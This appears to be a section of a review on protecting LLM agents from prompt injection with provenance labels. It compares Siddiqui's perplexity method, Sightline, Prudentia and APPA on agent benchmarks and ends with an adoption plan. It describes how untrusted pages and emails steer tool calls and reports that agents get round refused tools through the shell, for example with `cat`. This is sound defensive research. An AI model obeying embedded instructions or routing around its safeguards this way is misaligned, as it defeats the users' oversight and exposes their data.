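*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) cites a review of 21 research proposals and five commercial agents, which found that users often have to choose between repeated approvals and an automated reviewer they can't inspect. Requesting approval less often would ease that choice. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem*, Anthropic cut Claude Code's approval prompts by 84% by automatically approving commands that ran inside a sandbox. Labels can also reduce approval prompts if they identify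 actions that outside text couldn't have influenced.

### Dropping labels that didn't matter

Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, proposed keeping only the labels of inputs that the model needed for its answer. Their method first runs the model on everything. It then measures how likely the same answer would be if the model had seen only the trusted text. The measure is perplexity, which is high when a model finds a text surprising. For an answer of `n` tokens with probabilities `p₁` to `pₙ`:

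```
perplexity = (p₁ × p₂ × … × pₙ)^(−1/n)

accept the trusted text alone if
perplexity(trusted text only) − perplexity(all text) ≤ λ
```

The developer chooses the tolerance `λ`. If the trusted text passes at that tolerance, the framework discards the first answer, runs the model again without the untrusted text and labels the new answer trusted. In the example, the README correction is just as likely without the web page, so the framework can make that edit. The version number is much less likely without the page, so that edit stays untrusted.

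The second run keeps the method safe because the new answer does not depend on the attacker's words, even if the score is wrong or an attacker has manipulated it. The method takes more computing time and is sometimes less accurate, but it preserves this guarantee.

In a test with pairs of news articles, which assumed that a search had already found the right articles, the method relaxed the label in 39% to 57% of the cases where that was possible. In 19% to 23% of the cases where it relaxed the label, it had dropped an article that the answer needed. Siddiqui and colleagues used Llama 2 models, which are now several generations old.

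With only two labels, the extra work is small. With four to six label levels, the method could need 16 to 64 additional calls, according to an estimate by Zhong and colleagues, whose screener removes irrelevant text before the model call. Siddiqui and colleagues expect the search to stop much earlier in typical cases, especially when the levels have a strict order.

Sightline avoids the repeated calls by measuring how much attention a model gave each input in a recorded call. Attention is the mechanism that weights earlier tokens as the model produces the next one. In a transformer, the design behind most language models, it is the only way information passes from one token to another. Models also attend to text they don't use, so a classifier trained on labeled examples identifies which inputs affected the output. Sightline can use an open model to analyze a closed model's calls about as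 accurately, and the analysis takes 0.12 to 0.20 seconds per call.

Xu and colleagues proved that faint attention can't rule out an influence, so they set the classifier's threshold to miss, on average, no more than a chosen share of real influences. They tested Sightline on 120 steps from AgentDojo runs in which a small model, Qwen3-8B, was under attack. Sightline removed 50.0% of the label creep while missing 3.9% of real influences. The best of seven competing methods removed 38.3% of the creep. A rule that blocked consequential calls with untrusted labels stopped all 34 attack calls.

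Sightline's guarantee is weaker than that of ordinary label propagation, which misses nothing if the original labels are right. Its error rate is an average that applies only if new calls resemble those used to set the threshold, and attackers have a strong incentive to write text that doesn't. Zero out of 34 is also compatible with a true rate as high as about 8%. In another test, Sightline missed 5% of influences overall but 10.1% among the outputs that the model produced most confidently. A framework could recover the stronger guarantee by running the model again without the inputs that Sightline drops, as Siddiqui and colleagues do, but this requires a second call.

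### Showing the planning model the rules

Many refusals happen because the planning model has no information about which actions will make it lose access to tools. Prudentia, the agent that Kolluri and colleagues built on FIDES, adds each tool's rule to the tool's description and shows the model the labels. Before opening hidden text, the model must give a reason and list the calls it plans to make afterward. It may then finish the task without opening the text, for example by passing it to a quarantined model.

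The model can also prompt the user to endorse untrusted text. Suppose an untrusted email contains a to-do list with ten items, and each requires a tool that runs only in a trusted context. The user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten separate calls. If no restricted calls will follow, Prudentia can open the text without prompting the user.

Kolluri and colleagues counted the human interventions needed across all the AgentDojo tasks that each agent completed:

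| Model | Interventions, FIDES | Interventions, Prudentia | Completed without help, FIDES | Completed without help, Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 7.8 | 23.8 | 50.3% | 42.5% |
| o3-mini | 18.8 | 16.4 | 50.1% | 59.1% |
| o4-mini | 36.8 | 19.2 | 53.2% | 59.4% |
| GPT-5 | 41.3 | 7.3 | 57.1% | 72.7% |

The paper's headline figure, a reduction of up to 1.9 times compared with FIDES, comes from o4-mini. With GPT-5, the reduction was more than fivefold. GPT-4o did worse with the extra information, so the approach depends on a model that can plan around the rules. On GPT-4o, a task also cost about 1.9 to 2.5 times as much as with FIDES.

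Prudentia leaves the label checks unchanged, and the planning model can't skip them. Its weak point is endorsement, because if a user endorses a hostile email, every later call runs in a trusted context, whereas mistakenly approving a tool call lets through only that call. The experiments assumed that a person would stop every attack, which looks optimistic given how few dangerous commands Anthropic's testers caught. People may read one question about an email more carefully than ten questions about tool calls, but the experiments didn't test this with real reviewers.

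### APPA's unknown labels and temporary branches

APPA (Agentic Permissions Policy Algebra) addresses both missing labels and label creep. In the design by Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026), in *APPA*, a result from an unlabeled tool is neither trusted nor untrusted. APPA records its source as unresolved and lets the agent keep working. A context label therefore has two parts, the label that known sources establish and a list of sources that nobody has classified:

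```
(a, U) combined with (b, V) = (a ⊔ b, U ∪ V)
```

When the agent requests a sensitive action, APPA must resolve the source's label using a cast, which is approved code that assigns a definite label to an unresolved source. Each cast has a limit on how permissive a label it can assign. If no cast applies, or the cast fails, APPA refuses the call.

Suppose the triage agent's `fetch_page` has no label. The agent can read a page and compare it with the project's files without interruption. If it then requests `write_file`, APPA needs a trust label for the page. If a cast labels every web page untrusted and public, `write_file` fails but `post_comment` can still publish a reply. Without a cast, both calls fail.

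This makes APPA default-on for protected sinks, since unclassified content can't reach them. Unlike labeling everything untrusted, it lets developers postpone work on tools whose results never affect a sensitive action. A cast that wrongly labels hostile text trusted would still leave a gap in protection, though the cast's limit caps the damage.

APPA checks each call twice. Before the call, it calculates what the context label would become if the tool returned what its developer declared. This matters for tools that read and send in one step, such as a test tool that reads a confidential financial record and emails it. A check that considered only the context before the call would allow the email, because the agent hasn't read the record yet. After the call, APPA checks the actual result before adding it to the context.

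If a call would make the context more restrictive, the agent has to accept that explicitly or read the data in a temporary branch. The branch starts with a copy of the conversation and its label, so the agent can't remove the label from a secret it has already read by opening a branch. Data read in the branch affects only the branch's label.

In the version-number example, the agent would open the library's website in a branch and ask for three whole numbers within set limits, such as 4, 12 and 1. APPA rejects free text, so an instruction on the page can't return to the main conversation. If the project's developers have decided to trust values in this format, the main context stays trusted and all four edits go ahead. Without that decision, the numbers remain untrusted and the problem returns. Even with it, a hostile page could still supply the number of an old version with a known flaw.

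Discarding a branch removes its text but doesn't undo its actions. A message that the branch sent stays sent, and APPA keeps a record of it.

When APPA refuses a call, it lists the permitted next steps. The agent may have to complete a required earlier step, clean the data with an approved function, or ask an authority, which can be a person, a fixed rule or another model. Each approval covers one exact call and leaves the context label unchanged. Ten calls would therefore need ten approvals, where Prudentia might need one endorsement, but a careless approval would allow only one call.

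### What 6,600 test episodes showed

Kravchenko and colleagues ran 6,600 episodes with three models on AgentThreatBench, an existing benchmark with 24 tasks, and Bench-Corp, a set of 20 scenarios in a fictional company. In Bench-Corp, an agent has to keep working after it has read private or untrusted material. In half of the episodes, extra instructions encouraged the models to follow commands embedded in what they read.

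| Test | Tasks completed with APPA | Attacks with APPA | Tasks completed by a comparison agent | Attacks against the comparison agent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentThreatBench | 64.2% to 76.7% | 0 of 720 | 83.3% to 97.5% (no protection) | 11.7% to 66.7% |
| Bench-Corp | 87% to 91% | 0 of 600 | 88% to 93% (APPA with open rules) | 30% to 38% |

Across both tests, no attack succeeded in the 1,320 episodes with APPA's protection on. The attacks worked against agents without it. On AgentThreatBench, protection lowered completion by 14 to 28 percentage points, partly because the automatic scorer rejected correct answers that lacked an exact phrase. On Bench-Corp, it barely lowered completion.

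With one model, APPA completed 88.0% of Bench-Corp episodes, compared with 56.5% without temporary branches and 35.0% without the remedies attached to a refusal. No attack succeeded in any version, so blocking alone was enough for security in these tests. The branches and remedies accounted for most of the completed episodes.

The evidence has some weaknesses. Arseny Kravchenko, the corresponding author, gives an address at the company Archestra, and the team designed Bench-Corp to exercise APPA's own features. Two configurations modeled on FIDES completed only 36% to 46% of Bench-Corp tasks and let through 26% to 35% of attacks, but the team's policies for them left out many of the rules that the scenarios test, so the comparison is weak evidence about FIDES itself. The 1,320 episodes repeat 44 task designs, so they are not independent trials. None of the 20 Bench-Corp scenarios is listed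 as a test of unlabeled tools, so support for APPA's handling of them, its most useful feature for gradual adoption, comes mainly from proofs.

### An order of adoption

A team with a working agent can add labels in five steps that postpone most of the disruption until the team knows where it will come from.

| Step | Change | What to measure |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Label at one gateway | Every tool result gets a label, even if the label is "unknown" | Share of the prompt's text that arrives with a label |
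| 2. Log without blocking | Checks run and record what they would refuse | Would-be refusals per run, by source and by sink |
| 3. Label the noisiest trusted sources | Reviewed overrides cover content that outsiders can't write | Refusals that each override removes |
| 4. Enforce at the most harmful sinks | Checks on a few tools begin to block | Approvals per completed task, and how many bad requests reviewers catch |
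| 5. Reverse the default | Unlabeled content counts as untrusted, and tools without rules refuse in untrusted context | Failures caused by missing labels, and the number of overrides in force |

The gateway can be a proxy between the agent and its tool servers. For a coding agent that does most of its work through a shell, the gateway can be the shell itself, as in the Flowsh system by Kim and colleagues. Neither covers text that a template inserts, so the team should run the marker audit from the previous section before relying on the log. A gateway also can't provide temporary branches, which need control over what enters the model's prompt.

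The logging step gives no protection, so existing approvals and sandboxes should stay on. Many teams would have to start keeping records for this step, since only 20% of the developers in Wu and colleagues' survey logged or audited their agents' actions. The log should name the source that first made the context untrusted. Otherwise, one web page followed by 30 edits looks like 30 separate problems. An invented log from 200 runs of the triage agent might show:

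| Source | Would-be refusals | Who can write it | Treatment |
|---|---|---|---|
| Issue bodies | 310 | Anyone | Keep untrusted and read in a branch |
| The project's own documentation site | 140 | Maintainers | Label trusted |
| Build reports | 90 | Build system, but outsiders choose branch names | Label only the pass-or-fail field trusted |
| Other websites | 60 | Anyone | Keep untrusted |

Issue bodies cause the most refusals here, but an override for them would defeat the purpose of the labels. Labeling the documentation site may remove fewer than 140 refusals because some of those runs also read an issue later, so the team should recalculate the log with the new label instead of subtracting. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests that signed documentation or changes from an authenticated maintainer could also justify less restrictive labels.

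For each proposed set of labels, the team can calculate the share of tasks completed with at most `k` approvals, the measure Kolluri and colleagues used. A large gap between `k = 0` and `k = 3` means that many tasks would need one to three human approvals to succeed, and the log shows which sources to work on next.

Enforcement should begin with sinks that the agent rarely uses and that can do lasting harm, such as changes to the build configuration. Reviewers are more likely to read each request when requests are rare. The team can test whether they do by occasionally adding a harmless request that reviewers should reject. If reviewers approve most of these test requests, the sink should automatically block requests that would otherwise go to review.

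A framework needs to close all routes to the same effect together. In 77 of the 290 reports of file misuse, shell commands bypassed the rules that applied to an agent's built-in tools. For example, an agent that couldn't open a file with its reading tool could print it with `cat`. This can happen without an attacker, because agents commonly look for another way after a refusal. If a framework blocks `write_file` but leaves the shell unchecked, the agent can still write files through the shell.

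Reversing the default is the last step for existing tools, but new tools can start under the strict default immediately. Google did this when it exempted old web code by name and required new code to comply. After the switch, the number of overrides should level off. If it keeps growing, developers are probably using overrides to silence refusals, and the team should look for a branch or a narrower tool that would make the override unnecessary.

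Plain tool calling without provenance labels is enough when no outsider can write anything the agent reads, or when the agent has no tool that could leak or damage something. An agent that formats files written by a project's maintainers meets the first condition. An agent that summarizes public issues for a maintainer meets the second if it can't open web addresses, although a hostile issue could still make the summary misleading. Adding a tool can change whether an agent meets either condition, so the team should check both again whenever it adds one.
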